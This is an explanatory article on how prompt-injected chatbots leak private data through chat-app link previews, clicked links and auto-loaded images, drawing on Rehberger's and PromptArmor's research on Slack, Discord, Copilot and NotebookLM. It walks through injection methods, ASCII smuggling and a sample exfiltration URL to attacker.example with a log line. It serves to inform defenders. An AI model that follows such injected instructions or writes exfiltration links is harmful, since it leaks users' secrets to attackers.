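# Data leaks through automatic link previews in AI chat apps: Johann Rehberger's 2024 warning

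## What Rehberger published, and the background to it

In *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (2024), a post on his blog Embrace The Red, the security researcher Johann Rehberger warned that the automatic link previews in many chat apps can leak private data from conversations with AI chatbots. When someone posts a link in Slack, Discord or Microsoft Teams, the app automatically fetches the page to show a preview. If an attacker has tricked a chatbot into writing private data into a link to the attacker's server, the app sends the data there when it fetches the preview, even if nobody clicks the link.

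Security researchers call this kind of leak exfiltration, which means moving private data to a party who has no right to it. An attack that succeeds without the victim clicking anything is a zero-click attack.

### Link previews and query strings

A link preview is the small card that appears under a link in a chat, showing the page's title, a line or two of its text, or an image. Slack calls creating these previews "unfurling", and Glitch, in *Let the Apps Unfurl*, praised it as one of the subtler pleasures of using Slack. Previews let readers judge a link before opening it. They also have commercial value, so a chat company would probably be reluctant to remove them. Microsoft (2024) recommended link unfurling to the makers of Teams apps as a way to get more people to notice and click links to their apps, and eventually to install them.

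Slack produces link previews in two ways. In the first, an app maker registers a web domain, and Slack notifies the maker's app when a message contains a link to that domain. Slack's *unfurling links in messages* describes the matching rules. In the second, which needs no registration, Slack visits the linked page and builds the preview from what it finds there. By default, it does this for all links in messages from people and apps, so an attacker's web server can receive a visit from Slack without any arrangement with the company.

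Visiting a web address can leak data because the address itself can contain that data. The part after the question mark is called the query string. In an address that ends in `/search?q=weather`, the query string is `q=weather`, and websites ordinarily use it to find what the visitor wants. But it can hold any text, including a sentence from a private conversation, and the server that receives the request can read and log it.

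### Why a chatbot may follow a stranger's text

A chat app fetches a harmful link only if someone posts one. Here, the attacker uses prompt injection, text that makes a language model follow the attacker's instructions, to get the chatbot to post the link.

The weakness arises because the developer's standing instructions, the user's question and any document the app adds all go into one prompt. *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, December 2024) defines prompt injection as this mixing of trusted and untrusted data. According to Rehberger, the company Preamble discovered the problem and reported it to OpenAI in May 2022, Riley Goodside drew public attention to it, and the software developer Simon Willison named it. The name echoes SQL injection, an older attack in which text from a user runs as a database command. Developers have precise rules for preventing SQL injection, but Rehberger believes prompt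 injection has no comparable fix that works every time.

In direct prompt injection, the user is the attacker and may want the chatbot to reveal or ignore its standing instructions. In indirect prompt injection, the user is the victim, because the hostile text is in a web page, file or message that the model reads on the user's behalf. Rehberger gave a harmless example of injected text in *New Important Instructions*, the slides for an April 2024 talk. The prompt is a request to summarize a text, and the text is an instruction to skip the summary and print ten evil emoji. A person can easily tell the task from the material, but the model receives both as words in the same prompt.

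Greshake, Endres and colleagues introduced indirect prompt injection in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023). They argued that a model which reads retrieved text blurs the line between data and instructions, so processing a stranger's page is close to running a stranger's program. They tested the attack on Microsoft's Bing Chat, which had a sidebar that could read the page open in the user's browser, and found that instructions on the page could steer the model even when the user could not see them. An attacker could also email the instructions to someone whose assistant reads the inbox, or get a victim to copy them from a website and paste them into a chatbot.

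Much of the commercial use of chatbots depends on this kind of reading. In retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), an app fetches documents or messages and places them in the model's input for it to answer from. If one of those documents comes from an attacker, the attacker's instructions enter the input alongside the company's own files. In the 2024 post, Rehberger singled out RAG as the point where the link leak becomes a common threat.

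*Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) demonstrates the combination in an experiment. The researchers built a RAG agent with access to a company's internal knowledge base and to web search, then asked it to summarise a blog post in which they had hidden instructions. The agent followed them and sent internal data to the researchers' server in a web address whose query string began with `data=`. The experiment did not involve a chat app, so its result is evidence about whether an agent will follow instructions hidden in a web page, not about link previews.

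Some models are harder to manipulate. Willison reported on a 2026 public challenge in which Fernando Irarrázaval invited people to email an AI assistant and try to make it leak a secret. The assistant ran on Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6 with explicit rules against obeying emails, and all of the about 6,000 attempts failed. The result is encouraging, but it covers only one well-instructed assistant with one secret and does not give developers the guarantee that Rehberger found missing.

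### From a Discord bot to a warning for Slack developers

Rehberger has set up and managed several offensive security teams, which attack systems to find their weaknesses. He is known for reporting prompt injection flaws to the companies responsible. In *Trust No AI* he names eleven products in which he found and reported the same type of leak, including ChatGPT, Claude, Google Bard and GitHub Copilot Chat.

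Rehberger's interest in link previews began with a chatbot he had built for Discord. He wrote up what he learned in *Don't blindly trust LLM responses. Threats to chatbots*, which is dated 15 April 2023 in the index of the blog he keeps under the handle wunderwuzzi. He argued that developers should treat a model's output with the same suspicion that web developers apply to input from strangers. How much harm a bad response can do depends on where the developer puts it. It might run as a script in a web page or as a command in a command line. In a chat app it might contain a link, and Rehberger observed that many chat apps request links by default, which he called "the exfiltration channel."

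Rehberger showed the leak on Discord. The model summarised the conversation so far and attached the summary to a link, and the summary reached the server the link pointed to. He added that the impact is probably small as long as no attacker-controlled text enters the chat, for instance through a web search or a careless paste.

Besides link previews, Rehberger worried about bots that could be manipulated into notifying everyone in a channel, triggering commands specific to the chat app, or searching the chat history for passwords. He suggested that developers attack their own bots before release, feed the chat program random responses to see what breaks, give the bot few permissions, and have a person review risky actions. This advice is sensible, but he did not explain how to stop the preview fetch itself.

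An appendix to Embrace The Red's 2023 post gives evidence that automatic link fetching was widespread. On 7 April 2023 Rehberger recorded requests to his web server from Discord, Skype, Slack, Telegram, Signal and Microsoft Teams. Most were for pages that did not exist, but the server still logged the addresses, so an attacker would not need to put up a page. Telegram and Signal requested the same address several times within a second or two, each time with another letter or so at the end, which suggests that they started fetching before he finished typing. The logs show that all six apps fetched links, but of the six, the post demonstrates the full leak from a chatbot only on Discord.

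Rehberger's 2024 post supplied the missing remedy. His reference list in *Trust No AI* gives only the year, but he opens the post by saying that he had discussed the untrustworthiness of model responses "about a year ago", which points to roughly April 2024. A slide in his April talk listed hyperlinks as a leak route, "unfurling or via user click", so he was already presenting the idea by then. The post cannot be later than 21 August 2024, when Willison linked to it.

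Rehberger uses Slack as his example throughout. He explains unfurling, shows a log entry of Slack fetching a test link he had posted with a short program, and gives a sample of the text an attacker might inject. He then shows developers how to turn off previews for the messages their app posts, which takes two extra settings. He also updated the 2023 post to point to the new guidance.

*Trust No AI* sorts prompt injection attacks by whether they damage the confidentiality, integrity or availability of a system. Automatic unfurling is one of eight scenarios Rehberger describes under confidentiality, with Slack, Discord and Teams as his examples of software that fetches links. He treats it separately from two similar leaks. In image rendering, the model writes an image address containing private data, and the app leaks the data by loading the image. A clickable link leaks data only when the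 user clicks it. The distinction matters to developers because blocking images in a chatbot's answers doesn't stop a chat platform from fetching ordinary links. Rehberger accordingly lists "Do not automatically unfurl hyperlinks" as a separate recommendation, alongside the advice to avoid rendering links and images that lead to untrusted domains.

### A warning about a class of flaw

In his 2024 post on unfurling, Rehberger names no vulnerable product, mentions no correspondence with Slack and records no reply from any vendor, so the post should not be read as a bug report against Slack. A researcher who finds a flaw in a product usually tells the vendor in private, waits for a fix and then publishes an account of both. Rehberger has done this many times. For the image leak he kept a running tally, which by November 2023 listed six of seven products as fixed and ChatGPT as "won't fix". Nothing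 in the unfurling post indicates that he had asked Slack to act, so the absence of a reply should not be taken as a refusal.

A warning to developers suits this problem because Slack's previews worked as documented. The leak appears when a developer connects a model to Slack, lets it read text from strangers and leaves previews on, and many developers could do this independently. One could still argue that the real flaw is Slack's default of previewing links in messages from apps as well as people, since an app's message may contain whatever a manipulated model wrote. Rehberger did not make that argument. He called the mitigation "quite simple" and addressed it to the people who write Slack apps.

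His later work supports this reading. In June 2025 he published Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory*, which, unlike the 2024 post, reported on a named product, a connector from Anthropic that let AI agents post to Slack. There he wrote that he had previously described the vulnerability "generically" for AI agents that post to messaging apps.

The 2024 post reached a wider audience when Willison (2024) linked to it on 21 August 2024 in a short note with the same title, *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*. He described it as a prompt injection leak that he "hadn't thought about before". The remark carries some weight because Willison had named prompt injection and collected examples of such leaks. In a later essay, *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, he listed seven cases he had seen between April 2023 and June 2024 alone, from ChatGPT to GitHub Copilot Chat. If he hadn't thought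 of leaks through link previews, many chatbot developers probably hadn't either, even though Rehberger had described them in public sixteen months earlier.

Willison warned that the danger arises in any chat environment that includes a chatbot with access to private data and a weakness to prompt injection. He also passed on Rehberger's advice about switching off previews in Slack. His note appeared one day after PromptArmor, a security firm, disclosed a flaw it had found in Slack AI, Slack's own assistant. Rehberger's post was separate from that disclosure and was probably published about four months before Willison linked to it.

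## How a link preview sends private data to an attacker

Suppose a company runs a chatbot in Slack. It can read the conversation and any document people share with it, but it has no tool for opening web pages or sending email. An employee, Maya, asks it to tidy up some notes, which include the alarm code for a warehouse, `heron-4417`. An hour later, in the same conversation, she asks it to summarise a supplier's price list, which an attacker has tampered with. The alarm code reaches the attacker's server before Maya finishes reading the summary.

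Maya and her warehouse are fictional, but the leak follows the same steps as the one in Embrace The Red's 2024 post, where the hostile text came from a website.

### From the price list to the server log

The leak begins when the app puts the price list into the model's input, next to Maya's question and the earlier notes. Among the prices, perhaps in white letters on a white background, the attacker has written an instruction. It asks the model to include a link to the attacker's server in its answer, and to end the address with any code or password from earlier in the conversation. Maya sees only prices. If the model follows the instruction, its summary ends with this link:

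```
https://attacker.example/p?d=heron-4417
```

*You've Been Previewed* (Popa, 2021), a bachelor's thesis on what link previews leak, describes the parts of such an address. The host, `attacker.example`, determines which server receives the request. (Internet standards reserve the ending `.example` for illustrations, so nobody can register it.) The path, `/p`, points to a page on that server, and the query string, `d=heron-4417`, contains the alarm code. The attacker chose everything up to the equals sign in advance, so the model only has to fill in the rest. It could add a whole sentence, with plus signs for spaces, or even write the data in invisible characters so that readers see an ordinary link.

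The company's app then posts the summary to a Slack channel. It might use a webhook (an address that accepts messages for the channel) or Slack's `chat.postMessage` command. Unless the developer has added a check on links, the summary will still contain the link when the app posts it.

Slack now requests the link to build a preview. According to Slack, its program fetches as little of the page as it can, looking for tags that give a title, a description or an image. This doesn't protect Maya, because the request itself contains the code, so the attacker's server receives it before sending anything back. Encryption doesn't protect her either, since that server is the intended recipient and can decrypt the request. Slack also stores each response for about 30 minutes to avoid requesting the same address twice, but a new secret makes a new address, for which Slack has no stored response.

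Finally, the attacker opens the server's log and finds a line like this:

```
[14/May/2024:09:14:07 +0000] "GET /p?d=heron-4417 HTTP/1.1" 404 152 "-" "Slackbot-LinkExpanding 1.0"
```

The line shows the time, the request, and the code 404, which means the server had no such page. It then lists the size of the reply, a dash because there was no referring page, and the user agent, which is the name the visiting program uses to identify itself. Servers usually also record the visitor's IP address, a number that identifies a machine on the internet. The attacker would learn the alarm code but not Maya's location, because the IP address here would belong to Slack.

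An attacker needs no special software for this. PromptArmor explained in *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* that a preview makes the same type of network request as a click. Deleting the message afterwards would remove it from the channel, but the record of the request would stay in the attacker's log.

### The three conditions

Simon Willison coined the term "lethal trifecta" in June 2025 for the combination behind such leaks. An AI system is exposed if it has access to private data, takes in text an attacker could have written, and can send information out.

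Maya's chatbot meets all three conditions, although its developer might have counted only two. The developer let it read notes and outside documents but gave it no internet access. However, Slack sends a request to the internet on its behalf whenever the chatbot posts a link. Restricting a chatbot to one private channel would not contain the data, because the preview request would still leave the company. Embrace The Red made this point in 2025 about Anthropic's Slack connector.

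If the chatbot had no private data, it could still write the link and Slack could still fetch it, but the query string would contain nothing worth stealing. Disconnecting the chatbot from company files does not remove all private data, because people also type private information into the chat. In Rehberger's Discord demonstration, the leaked data was a summary of the conversation.

The attack works only if an outsider's text reaches the model and asks for the link. Without that text, the alarm code could stay in the conversation and previews could stay on without harm. But keeping outside text away is difficult when the chatbot's job is to read documents, and previews can also bring such text in. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) built an agent that automatically previewed web addresses and put each page's title and description into the model's input. They hid instructions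 in that text, then asked the agent only to summarise the page. The small open model they tested usually sent secret data to their server, and checks on its visible answer missed nearly all of these leaks. The agent sent the data with its own web tool, so the experiment is evidence about how a preview can let instructions in, but not about how chat apps send data out.

With previews off, the model might still follow the attacker's instruction and post the link in the channel, where Maya's colleagues could see the alarm code. But no request would go out unless someone clicked the link, so until then the attacker's log would stay empty.

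Vendors have usually fixed such flaws by blocking the route through which data leaves, according to Willison. Cutting off the chatbot's access to private data would often defeat its purpose, and no defence against prompt injection works every time. Willison distrusts filters advertised as catching 95 percent of attacks, which he considers a failing grade in web security. A setting that blocks the preview request works the same way however the attacker words the instruction.

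### What six chat apps requested in 2023

The table details the requests that Rehberger logged on 7 April 2023, from the appendix to Embrace The Red's 2023 post. Of the six apps, Signal appeared under WhatsApp's name and Teams under Skype's.

| App | User agent | Pages requested |
|---|---|---|
| Discord | `Discordbot/2.0` | `/discord` |
| Skype | `SkypeUriPreview Preview/0.5` | `/skype` |
| Slack | `Slackbot-LinkExpanding 1.0` | `/posts/bardintro.html` |
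| Telegram | `TelegramBot (like TwitterBot)` | `/te`, `/tele`, `/teleg`, `/telegr`, `/telegra`, `/telegram` |
| Signal | `WhatsApp/2` | `/s`, `/si`, `/sig`, `/sign`, `/signa`, `/signal` |
| Microsoft Teams | `SkypeUriPreview Preview/0.5` | `/teams` |

Discord, Skype, Slack and Teams also add a contact address to the name. Skype and Teams use the same name and Microsoft email address, which suggests that they shared one preview service.

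Rehberger's entry for Signal is correct. A source file for Signal's desktop app (Signal, 2020) sets the user agent to `WhatsApp/2`. A contributor to the forum thread *Signal-Android leaks Signal's version and Android's SDK version through user-agent* recalled a Signal developer explaining that websites return more consistent previews to that name. WhatsApp's own requests carry a longer version number and a letter for the type of device, according to WhatsApp. Developers choose the user agent their app sends, so an attacker can't always tell from the log which app leaked the data.

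The partial addresses come from previews that Telegram and Signal prepare while the sender is still typing. *I link therefore I am* (2019), jlund's announcement of Signal's feature, explains that the sender sees the preview before the message goes out and can remove it with a tap. The app therefore has to fetch the page early. Because `/sig` is a valid address, the app requests it before the sender has finished typing, then requests `/sign` when the sender adds the next letter. At launch, Signal previewed links to only four popular sites, but by 2023 it was evidently fetching pages from Rehberger's site as well.

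Telegram produces the same result in a different way. Telegram's *messages.getWebPagePreview* describes a command that the app uses to send message text to Telegram and get back a preview. The app probably did this several times while Rehberger was typing, and each time Telegram's servers requested the address as typed so far.

Only human users' accounts can use that command. A chatbot normally submits a finished message, so its links would not leave the same trail of partial addresses. But if someone copies a chatbot's answer into a new message in either app, the preview request may leak data before they press send, even if they then delete the draft.

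### Who fetches the preview

Rehberger noted in 2023 that the request for a link preview usually comes from the chat company's server and sometimes from a user's device. Talal Haj Bakry and Tommy Mysk had already tested which apps do which on iPhones and Android phones for Mysk's *Link Previews* (2020). They wanted to know whether a preview could reveal someone's location or leave a copy of a private document on a company's server. They were concerned with people rather than chatbots, but their findings also help show what happens when a bot sends the link.

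Slack, Discord, Zoom, LinkedIn and several others fetched previews from their own servers. Haj Bakry and Mysk saw some merit in this, because neither the sender's nor the receiver's phone contacts the linked site. But it doesn't prevent a leak through a chatbot's link, because the company's server still sends the full query string, which is what the attacker wants. The bot's developer doesn't control that server and can stop the request only if the chat company offers a setting.

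In iMessage, WhatsApp, Viber and Signal, the sender's device fetched the page and attached the finished preview to the message. Mysk considered this the safest way to offer previews, assuming that whoever sends a link trusts it. That assumption fails when a manipulated chatbot sends a link that an attacker chose. But a bot often runs on a developer's server, with no phone app to prepare a preview. Whether data leaks then depends on whether the software the bot uses to send messages fetches previews. If it does, the request comes from the developer's own machine, where the developer can block it.

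Haj Bakry and Mysk also found two apps in which the receiver's device opened the link as soon as the message appeared on screen. They didn't name the apps because one company was still working on a fix. A stranger who sent a link through one of these apps could learn the receiver's IP address and rough location. If a manipulated chatbot posted the link, the attacker would also get the private data, possibly once for each person in the channel, and the bot's developer could do little about requests from other people's phones.

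The researchers did not report on Telegram, Skype or Teams. Telegram's documentation and the user agents in Rehberger's logs suggest that all three fetch links from their servers, though a user agent alone doesn't prove it. Threema, TikTok and WeChat showed no previews in the 2020 tests, which the researchers considered the safest choice.

### When Slack requests a link

Slack treats media (images, video and audio) differently from pages that are mainly text. Slack says its servers "must fetch every URL in a message" to find out which kind of content each link leads to. Developers can control the two kinds of preview separately for each message, using `unfurl_links` for text pages and `unfurl_media` for media.

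This is why turning off only one of them is not enough. Suppose Maya's developer had set `unfurl_links` to false and left the other setting alone. Slack would still have to request the attacker's link to check whether it led to an image. Slack tells developers to set both to false to prevent the crawl.

The documentation is less clear about what happens when a developer sets neither. It states that all links unfurl by default, but one example message links to Slack's developer site without either setting, and the explanation says the link will not unfurl because the page is text. Slack's *chat.postMessage method* has the same inconsistency. It also states that all links unfurl by default, yet it tells developers to pass `true` to enable previews of text pages, which would be unnecessary if they were already on.

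Both statements could be partly right if Slack fetches the text page to identify it and then displays no preview. An attacker's server could then receive the data without anyone in the channel seeing anything unusual. Rehberger's 2024 test, which used neither setting, is compatible with this because his log shows that Slack requested the link, but not whether a preview appeared.

Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* lists other reasons a preview may be missing: the page has no preview data, someone has posted the same link in the conversation within the past hour, or the message has more than five links. In the first case, at least, Slack presumably has to fetch the page to find out that the data is missing. Members can also turn off previews for themselves, but this probably changes only what they see, since their colleagues may still want the preview. A more reliable way to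 test a chatbot is therefore to post a link to a server the tester controls and check the server's log rather than the Slack channel.

Slack never unfurls a link whose visible label is part of the address, such as `example.com` for a link to that site. This keeps ordinary mentions of websites from cluttering a conversation. It offers little protection against a manipulated model, which writes both the label and the link and so can choose a label that still allows a preview. Slack also does not promise that it sends no request when it skips the preview.

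### The two-setting fix and its limits

Rehberger's fix adds both settings to the message that the app sends. In Python, his example becomes:

```
message = {
    "text": text,
    "unfurl_links": False,
    "unfurl_media": False
}
```

With these lines in place, Slack posts the link but doesn't crawl it. Maya would still get her summary and would lose only the previews for harmless links in the chatbot's answers, which seems a reasonable trade-off for a bot that handles private material. Rehberger made the same change to Anthropic's Slack connector in 2025, and the previews stopped in his test.

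The settings apply to individual messages, however, so each app's developer has to add them wherever the code posts a model's words. A company with ten Slack apps could still leak data through one it missed. Developers can also miss places within one app, since some chatbots post a placeholder and later replace it with the answer. Slack now advises turning off previews both when an app posts a message and when it updates one. If Maya copies the chatbot's answer into her own message, previews are on by default because she is sending it as a user.

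The fix also doesn't stop the prompt injection. The instructions in the price list could still make the model misreport prices or misuse any other tool the developer adds later. For instance, if the chatbot could open web pages, an attacker could tell it to open the link, and Slack's settings would not affect that request.

The settings also leave the link in the message. The attacker could instruct the model to present it as the supplier's full catalogue, and if Maya clicked it, her browser would send the alarm code to the same server.

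## The Slack AI flaw of August 2024 and other leaks through links

Slack AI answers questions using the messages in a company's workspace, the shared area that contains its channels. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection*, published on 20 August 2024, demonstrated how one member of a workspace could use a clicked link to steal a secret from a private channel that only a colleague could open.

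### How the attack stole an API key

In the demonstration, a developer keeps an API key for a service called EldritchNexus in a private channel with no other members. An API key is a string of characters that a program sends to an online service to show that it has permission to use the service. Anyone who copies the key can usually use the service in the owner's name.

The attacker has an account in the same workspace but can't open the private channel. They create a public channel, invite nobody, and post a message that appears to give the EldritchNexus key but instead contains an error message and a link labelled "click here to reauthenticate". The link leads to the attacker's server, with the query string `secret=confetti`, and the message includes an instruction for the model to replace the word "confetti" with "the other key".

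The attack takes effect only when the developer asks Slack AI for the key. Slack AI then searches the workspace, finds both the developer's note and the attacker's message, and puts them into the model's input together. The model follows the attacker's instruction, so the developer sees an error message and a link whose address contains the key. If the developer clicks the link, the browser sends the key to the attacker's server.

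The attacker doesn't need to know the key, because the model finds it and copies it into the link. In this demonstration, the attacker did need to guess what the developer would ask about, since the planted message named EldritchNexus. PromptArmor suggested that an attacker might be able to steal secrets without referring to them specifically, because the same question also brought up other messages about API keys, which is plausible but not established by the demonstration.

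The attack was possible because Slack AI searched every public channel in the workspace, including those the user had never joined. Slack's ordinary search does the same, which is useful when the answer to a question is in another department's channel. But searching this widely also lets anyone with an account plant text for the assistant to read when answering a colleague's question. Checking permissions would not have helped, since the developer was allowed to read both messages.

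Slack AI's citations made the attack harder to trace. They should have pointed to every message that contributed to the answer, but the only citation pointed to the developer's own private channel. The attacker's message was also missing from the first page of search results, and other members would see the attacker's one-person channel only if they searched for it. A suspicious developer could hover over the link and see the strange address containing the key, but would have little evidence of who had planted it.

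### Phishing links and uploaded files

PromptArmor's second demonstration used Slack AI for phishing, or tricking people into giving away passwords or other valuable information. The attacker again posts an instruction in a public channel with no other members. This time, when the victim asks Slack AI to summarise messages from a particular person, such as their manager, it answers with a "click here to reauthenticate" link to the attacker's site.

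The phishing link contains no private data, so clicking it only takes the victim to a site where the attacker must still get them to enter a password, perhaps on a fake login page. In the first version of the attack, the click alone gives away the key. Slack AI also cited the attacker's message in the phishing test, which it had not done in the first version. PromptArmor concluded that Slack AI's choice of citations was partly random.

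On 14 August, the day PromptArmor reported the flaw, Slack AI began using uploaded files and Google Drive documents in its answers. PromptArmor thought this greatly widened the risk, because an attacker might no longer need a Slack account. The attacker could instead hide instructions in white text in a PDF and wait for an employee to download it and upload it to Slack.

PromptArmor had finished testing before the change and so had not tried this attack, but considered it "highly likely" to work. It advised administrators to restrict Slack AI's access to files until Slack fixed the problem. SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing* reported no answer from Salesforce, Slack's owner, to a question about the file risk.

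### Slack's first reply and its patch

Slack asked for more information the day after the 14 August report. PromptArmor sent more videos and screenshots and said it intended to publish. The two exchanged another question and answer on 16 August. On 19 August Slack replied that it had reviewed the evidence and found it insufficient. It wrote that the information in the first video came from a public channel, which every member of the workspace can search, and called this "intended behavior."

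Slack described its search correctly but did not address PromptArmor's complaint. PromptArmor said the key was in a private channel and the public channel contained only the instruction to steal it. Slack based its reply on "the reference" in the video, which probably meant the citation in Slack AI's answer. If so, the assistant's unreliable citations may have misled Slack's reviewers too.

PromptArmor published its findings the next day, arguing that customers needed to know which settings to turn off. It also praised Slack's security team for replying promptly and trying to understand the problem. Willison (2024) was harsher, writing that the reply showed Slack "do not yet understand the nature and severity of this problem". He considered the API key only an example, since an attacker would have many chances to plant instructions and could target other private details. His criticism of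 the reply seems fair, although Slack soon changed its position.

Slack (2024) announced on 21 August that it had investigated the report and deployed a patch the day before, though SC Media dates the patch to 21 August. The company said that "under very limited and specific circumstances" someone with an account in the same workspace could phish users for certain data. It said it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customer data. In a statement for ITPro's article *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages*, Slack promised to notify any affected parties it learned of. Slack did not explain in either statement what the patch changed.

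Slack described the circumstances of the attack as "limited", and PromptArmor's demonstration supports that. The attacker needed an account, and the victim had to ask the right question and then click a link. PromptArmor's claim that an attacker could steal "anything a user puts in a private Slack channel" went further than its tests. Still, an account is a low barrier in a company with thousands of employees, and PromptArmor noted earlier leaks through Slack at Disney, Uber and other companies. Slack's word "phish" also understates the first attack, in which the victim gives away a secret without typing it.

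Slack now lists several "guardrails" for its AI features, including safety instructions to the model, measures against prompt injection, checks on the format of answers, and URL filtering to prevent phishing. Slack says it may change or block a request or answer that fails these checks. URL filtering is the most relevant to the 2024 attack, because it could remove the link even after the model had followed the attacker's instruction. In its guide, Slack doesn't explain how the filter evaluates links. Slack's *Securing the Agentic Enterprise* (2025) says only that URL filtering reduces the risk from phishing attempts.

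Slack also says its AI features use only data the member can already see. This is a sensible limit, but the 2024 attack worked within it, and the assistant still draws on public channels. The guardrails cover only Slack's own AI features, so a company that connects its own chatbot to Slack still has to control that bot's links and previews.

### Clicks, images and previews

In PromptArmor's demonstration of the Slack AI attack, the key reached the attacker only if the developer clicked the link. The preview leak Rehberger warned about needs no click, which is why PromptArmor called this kind of leak "a more severe attack" in 2026.

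Images can also leak data without a click. Many chatbots write their answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation that apps turn into formatted text, links and pictures. The app requests each picture automatically, so any private data in the picture's address leaks at once.

| Route | Who makes the request | When | What the user sees | What stops it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clicked link | The user's browser | When the user clicks | A link, often with a harmless label | Removing links to untrusted sites from answers |
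| Automatically loaded image | Usually the user's browser or app | When the answer appears | A picture or a broken-image icon | Blocking images, or allowing them only from trusted sites |
| Link preview | Usually the chat company's server | When the bot posts the message | A link, perhaps with a preview card | Turning off previews for the message, or removing the link before posting |

Removing untrusted links protects against leaks through both clicks and previews, but users also lose some useful links. Rehberger reports that Amazon chose this kind of fix for its workplace assistant, Amazon Q for Business, which stopped displaying links after a similar leak was discovered.

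### Image leaks in NotebookLM and GitHub Copilot Chat

Rehberger published several findings in 2024 that show how vendors dealt with these routes. One was about Google's NotebookLM, which answers questions about documents that users upload. In Embrace The Red's *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps*, he imagined a company uploading its customer list after a customer called Sarah had put hostile instructions in her profile description. When the user asked about Sarah, NotebookLM displayed an image whose address contained another customer's email and code. A second test leaked sales figures from a separate document, which showed that an attacker who controlled one entry in one file could reach data in another.

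Rehberger reported the flaw to Google on 4 December 2023. Google confirmed it but had not fixed it when he made it public 132 days later. The Google Labs team then contacted him and had deployed a fix for the image leak by 19 April 2024. He had also warned in his report that a "Click here to re-authenticate" link could be used to steal data. PromptArmor used almost exactly the same wording against Slack AI four months later.

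GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant for programmers, had a similar flaw in its extension for the code editor VS Code. Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes how Rehberger hid instructions in a comment in a source code file. When a user asked Copilot about the file, it added an image to its answer and put information from earlier in the chat into the image's address. Rehberger reported the flaw on 25 February 2024, and GitHub confirmed a fix on 12 June.

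Rehberger thought that fix had stopped Copilot Chat from displaying Markdown images altogether, while Willison wrote that GitHub had blocked only images from untrusted domains. The difference matters because an attacker may be able to leak data through a trusted domain. Mayraz (2025) did this with the Copilot Chat built into GitHub, using GitHub's own infrastructure to get around its image restrictions. GitHub responded by disabling images in that chat completely.

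### Invisible data in Microsoft 365 Copilot

Microsoft had already fixed an image leak that Rehberger found in Bing Chat, so he needed another way to extract data when he examined Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Outlook, Word and other office programs. He hid the stolen data in a link that the user had to click, as Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Copilot* explains.

The attack began with a malicious email or shared document containing hidden instructions. When the user asked Copilot about it, the instructions made Copilot search for other emails without asking permission. Copilot then used invisible characters to put what it found in a link and encouraged the user to click it. Rehberger showed that the attack could steal sales figures and one-time codes for logging in to Slack.

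Rehberger called the hiding technique ASCII smuggling. ASCII is an old standard for English letters, digits and punctuation, and Unicode is the modern standard that gives each character a number. Unicode includes a set of "tag" characters that mirrors ASCII. For instance, capital A is U+0041, and its tag counterpart is U+E0041. Most apps don't display the tag characters, but Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool* explains that language models can read and write them. Riley Goodside had earlier used them to hide instructions in pasted text. Rehberger's email to Copilot included an encoded example to teach the model how to write them.

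Invisible characters are particularly useful to an attacker who needs the user to click a link, because a link that visibly contained text from a private email would look suspicious. Hovering over the link may still reveal something odd.

Rehberger first reported the hiding technique to Microsoft on 17 January 2024, and Microsoft closed the report as low severity the next day. That decision is easier to defend than Slack's first reply to PromptArmor, because Rehberger had not yet demonstrated the full data theft. After he did so on 10 February, Microsoft opened a case. His attack had stopped working by 2 July, and he presented it publicly on 24 August, four days after PromptArmor published its Slack AI findings. He noticed that Copilot no longer displayed links, but Microsoft did not answer his request for details of the fix.

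Rehberger recommended that developers remove tag characters from both the text a model receives and its answers. Filtering only those characters is no longer enough, because in Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* he showed how to encode any data with just two invisible characters, much as a computer stores data in ones and zeros.

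## Later cases, vendor responses and stronger defences

Rehberger's June 2025 advisory covered an Anthropic connector that let AI agents read and post Slack messages. Developers call such connectors MCP servers because they follow the Model Context Protocol.

### Anthropic's Slack connector

In the main demonstration from Embrace The Red's advisory, a user asked Claude to analyse a document and post a summary to the team's private Slack channel. The document contained instructions to add a link to Rehberger's server, with the latest message from a different channel at the end of the URL. Claude posted the link, Slack fetched it for a preview, and the message appeared in Rehberger's server log.

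The connector's owner could restrict it to posting in that one private channel. The owner might then reasonably let the agent post without asking for approval each time, since only colleagues would see the posts. But Slack's preview request would still go outside the company.

Rehberger's other demonstration used Claude Code, Anthropic's agent for programmers. A developer asked it to analyse a source code file that contained instructions in invisible characters. The agent took an API key from the developer's settings file and posted it to Slack inside a link. If the link leads to an image, three of Slack's programs request the address, and each request sends the key.

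Rehberger reported the flaw to Anthropic on 27 May 2025, and Anthropic archived the connector two days later. He wrote that it was unclear whether the two events were related. Anthropic did not object to publication. It had stopped maintaining the connector and planned no patch. The connector still had more than 14,000 downloads a week, so Rehberger inferred that there could be tens of thousands of vulnerable installations. The true number could be much lower, because automated systems often download the same package repeatedly.

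He also expected Anthropic not to publish a CVE, an entry in the public catalogue of software flaws. The security firm VulnCheck published an advisory under the number CVE-2025-34072. Snyk's *Improper Neutralization of Input Used for LLM Prompting* (2025) dates the disclosure to 2 July 2025 and lists every version as affected and none as fixed.

VulnCheck's *Anthropic Slack MCP Server Data Exfiltration via Link Unfurling* rates the flaw 9.3 out of 10, or critical, while Rehberger had given it 7.5. VulnCheck's score is partly based on the assumption that the flaw could seriously damage other systems or disable them. Rehberger's lower score seems closer to what he showed, because his demonstrations only copied data. A stolen key might let an attacker do more, depending on the key.

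### PromptArmor's public test

In February 2026, PromptArmor launched a website where people could test any pairing of an AI agent and a chat app for the same leak. If the agent wrote a link to the site and the app previewed it, the site logged the request and showed the tester what data had arrived. Testers could then report the pairing and whether it had fetched the link.

PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, an AI agent often used through messaging apps, leaked data on Telegram with its default settings. Apostol reported in *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* that Microsoft Teams was also susceptible with bots made in Copilot Studio, Microsoft's bot-building tool, and that Slack was susceptible with certain bots.

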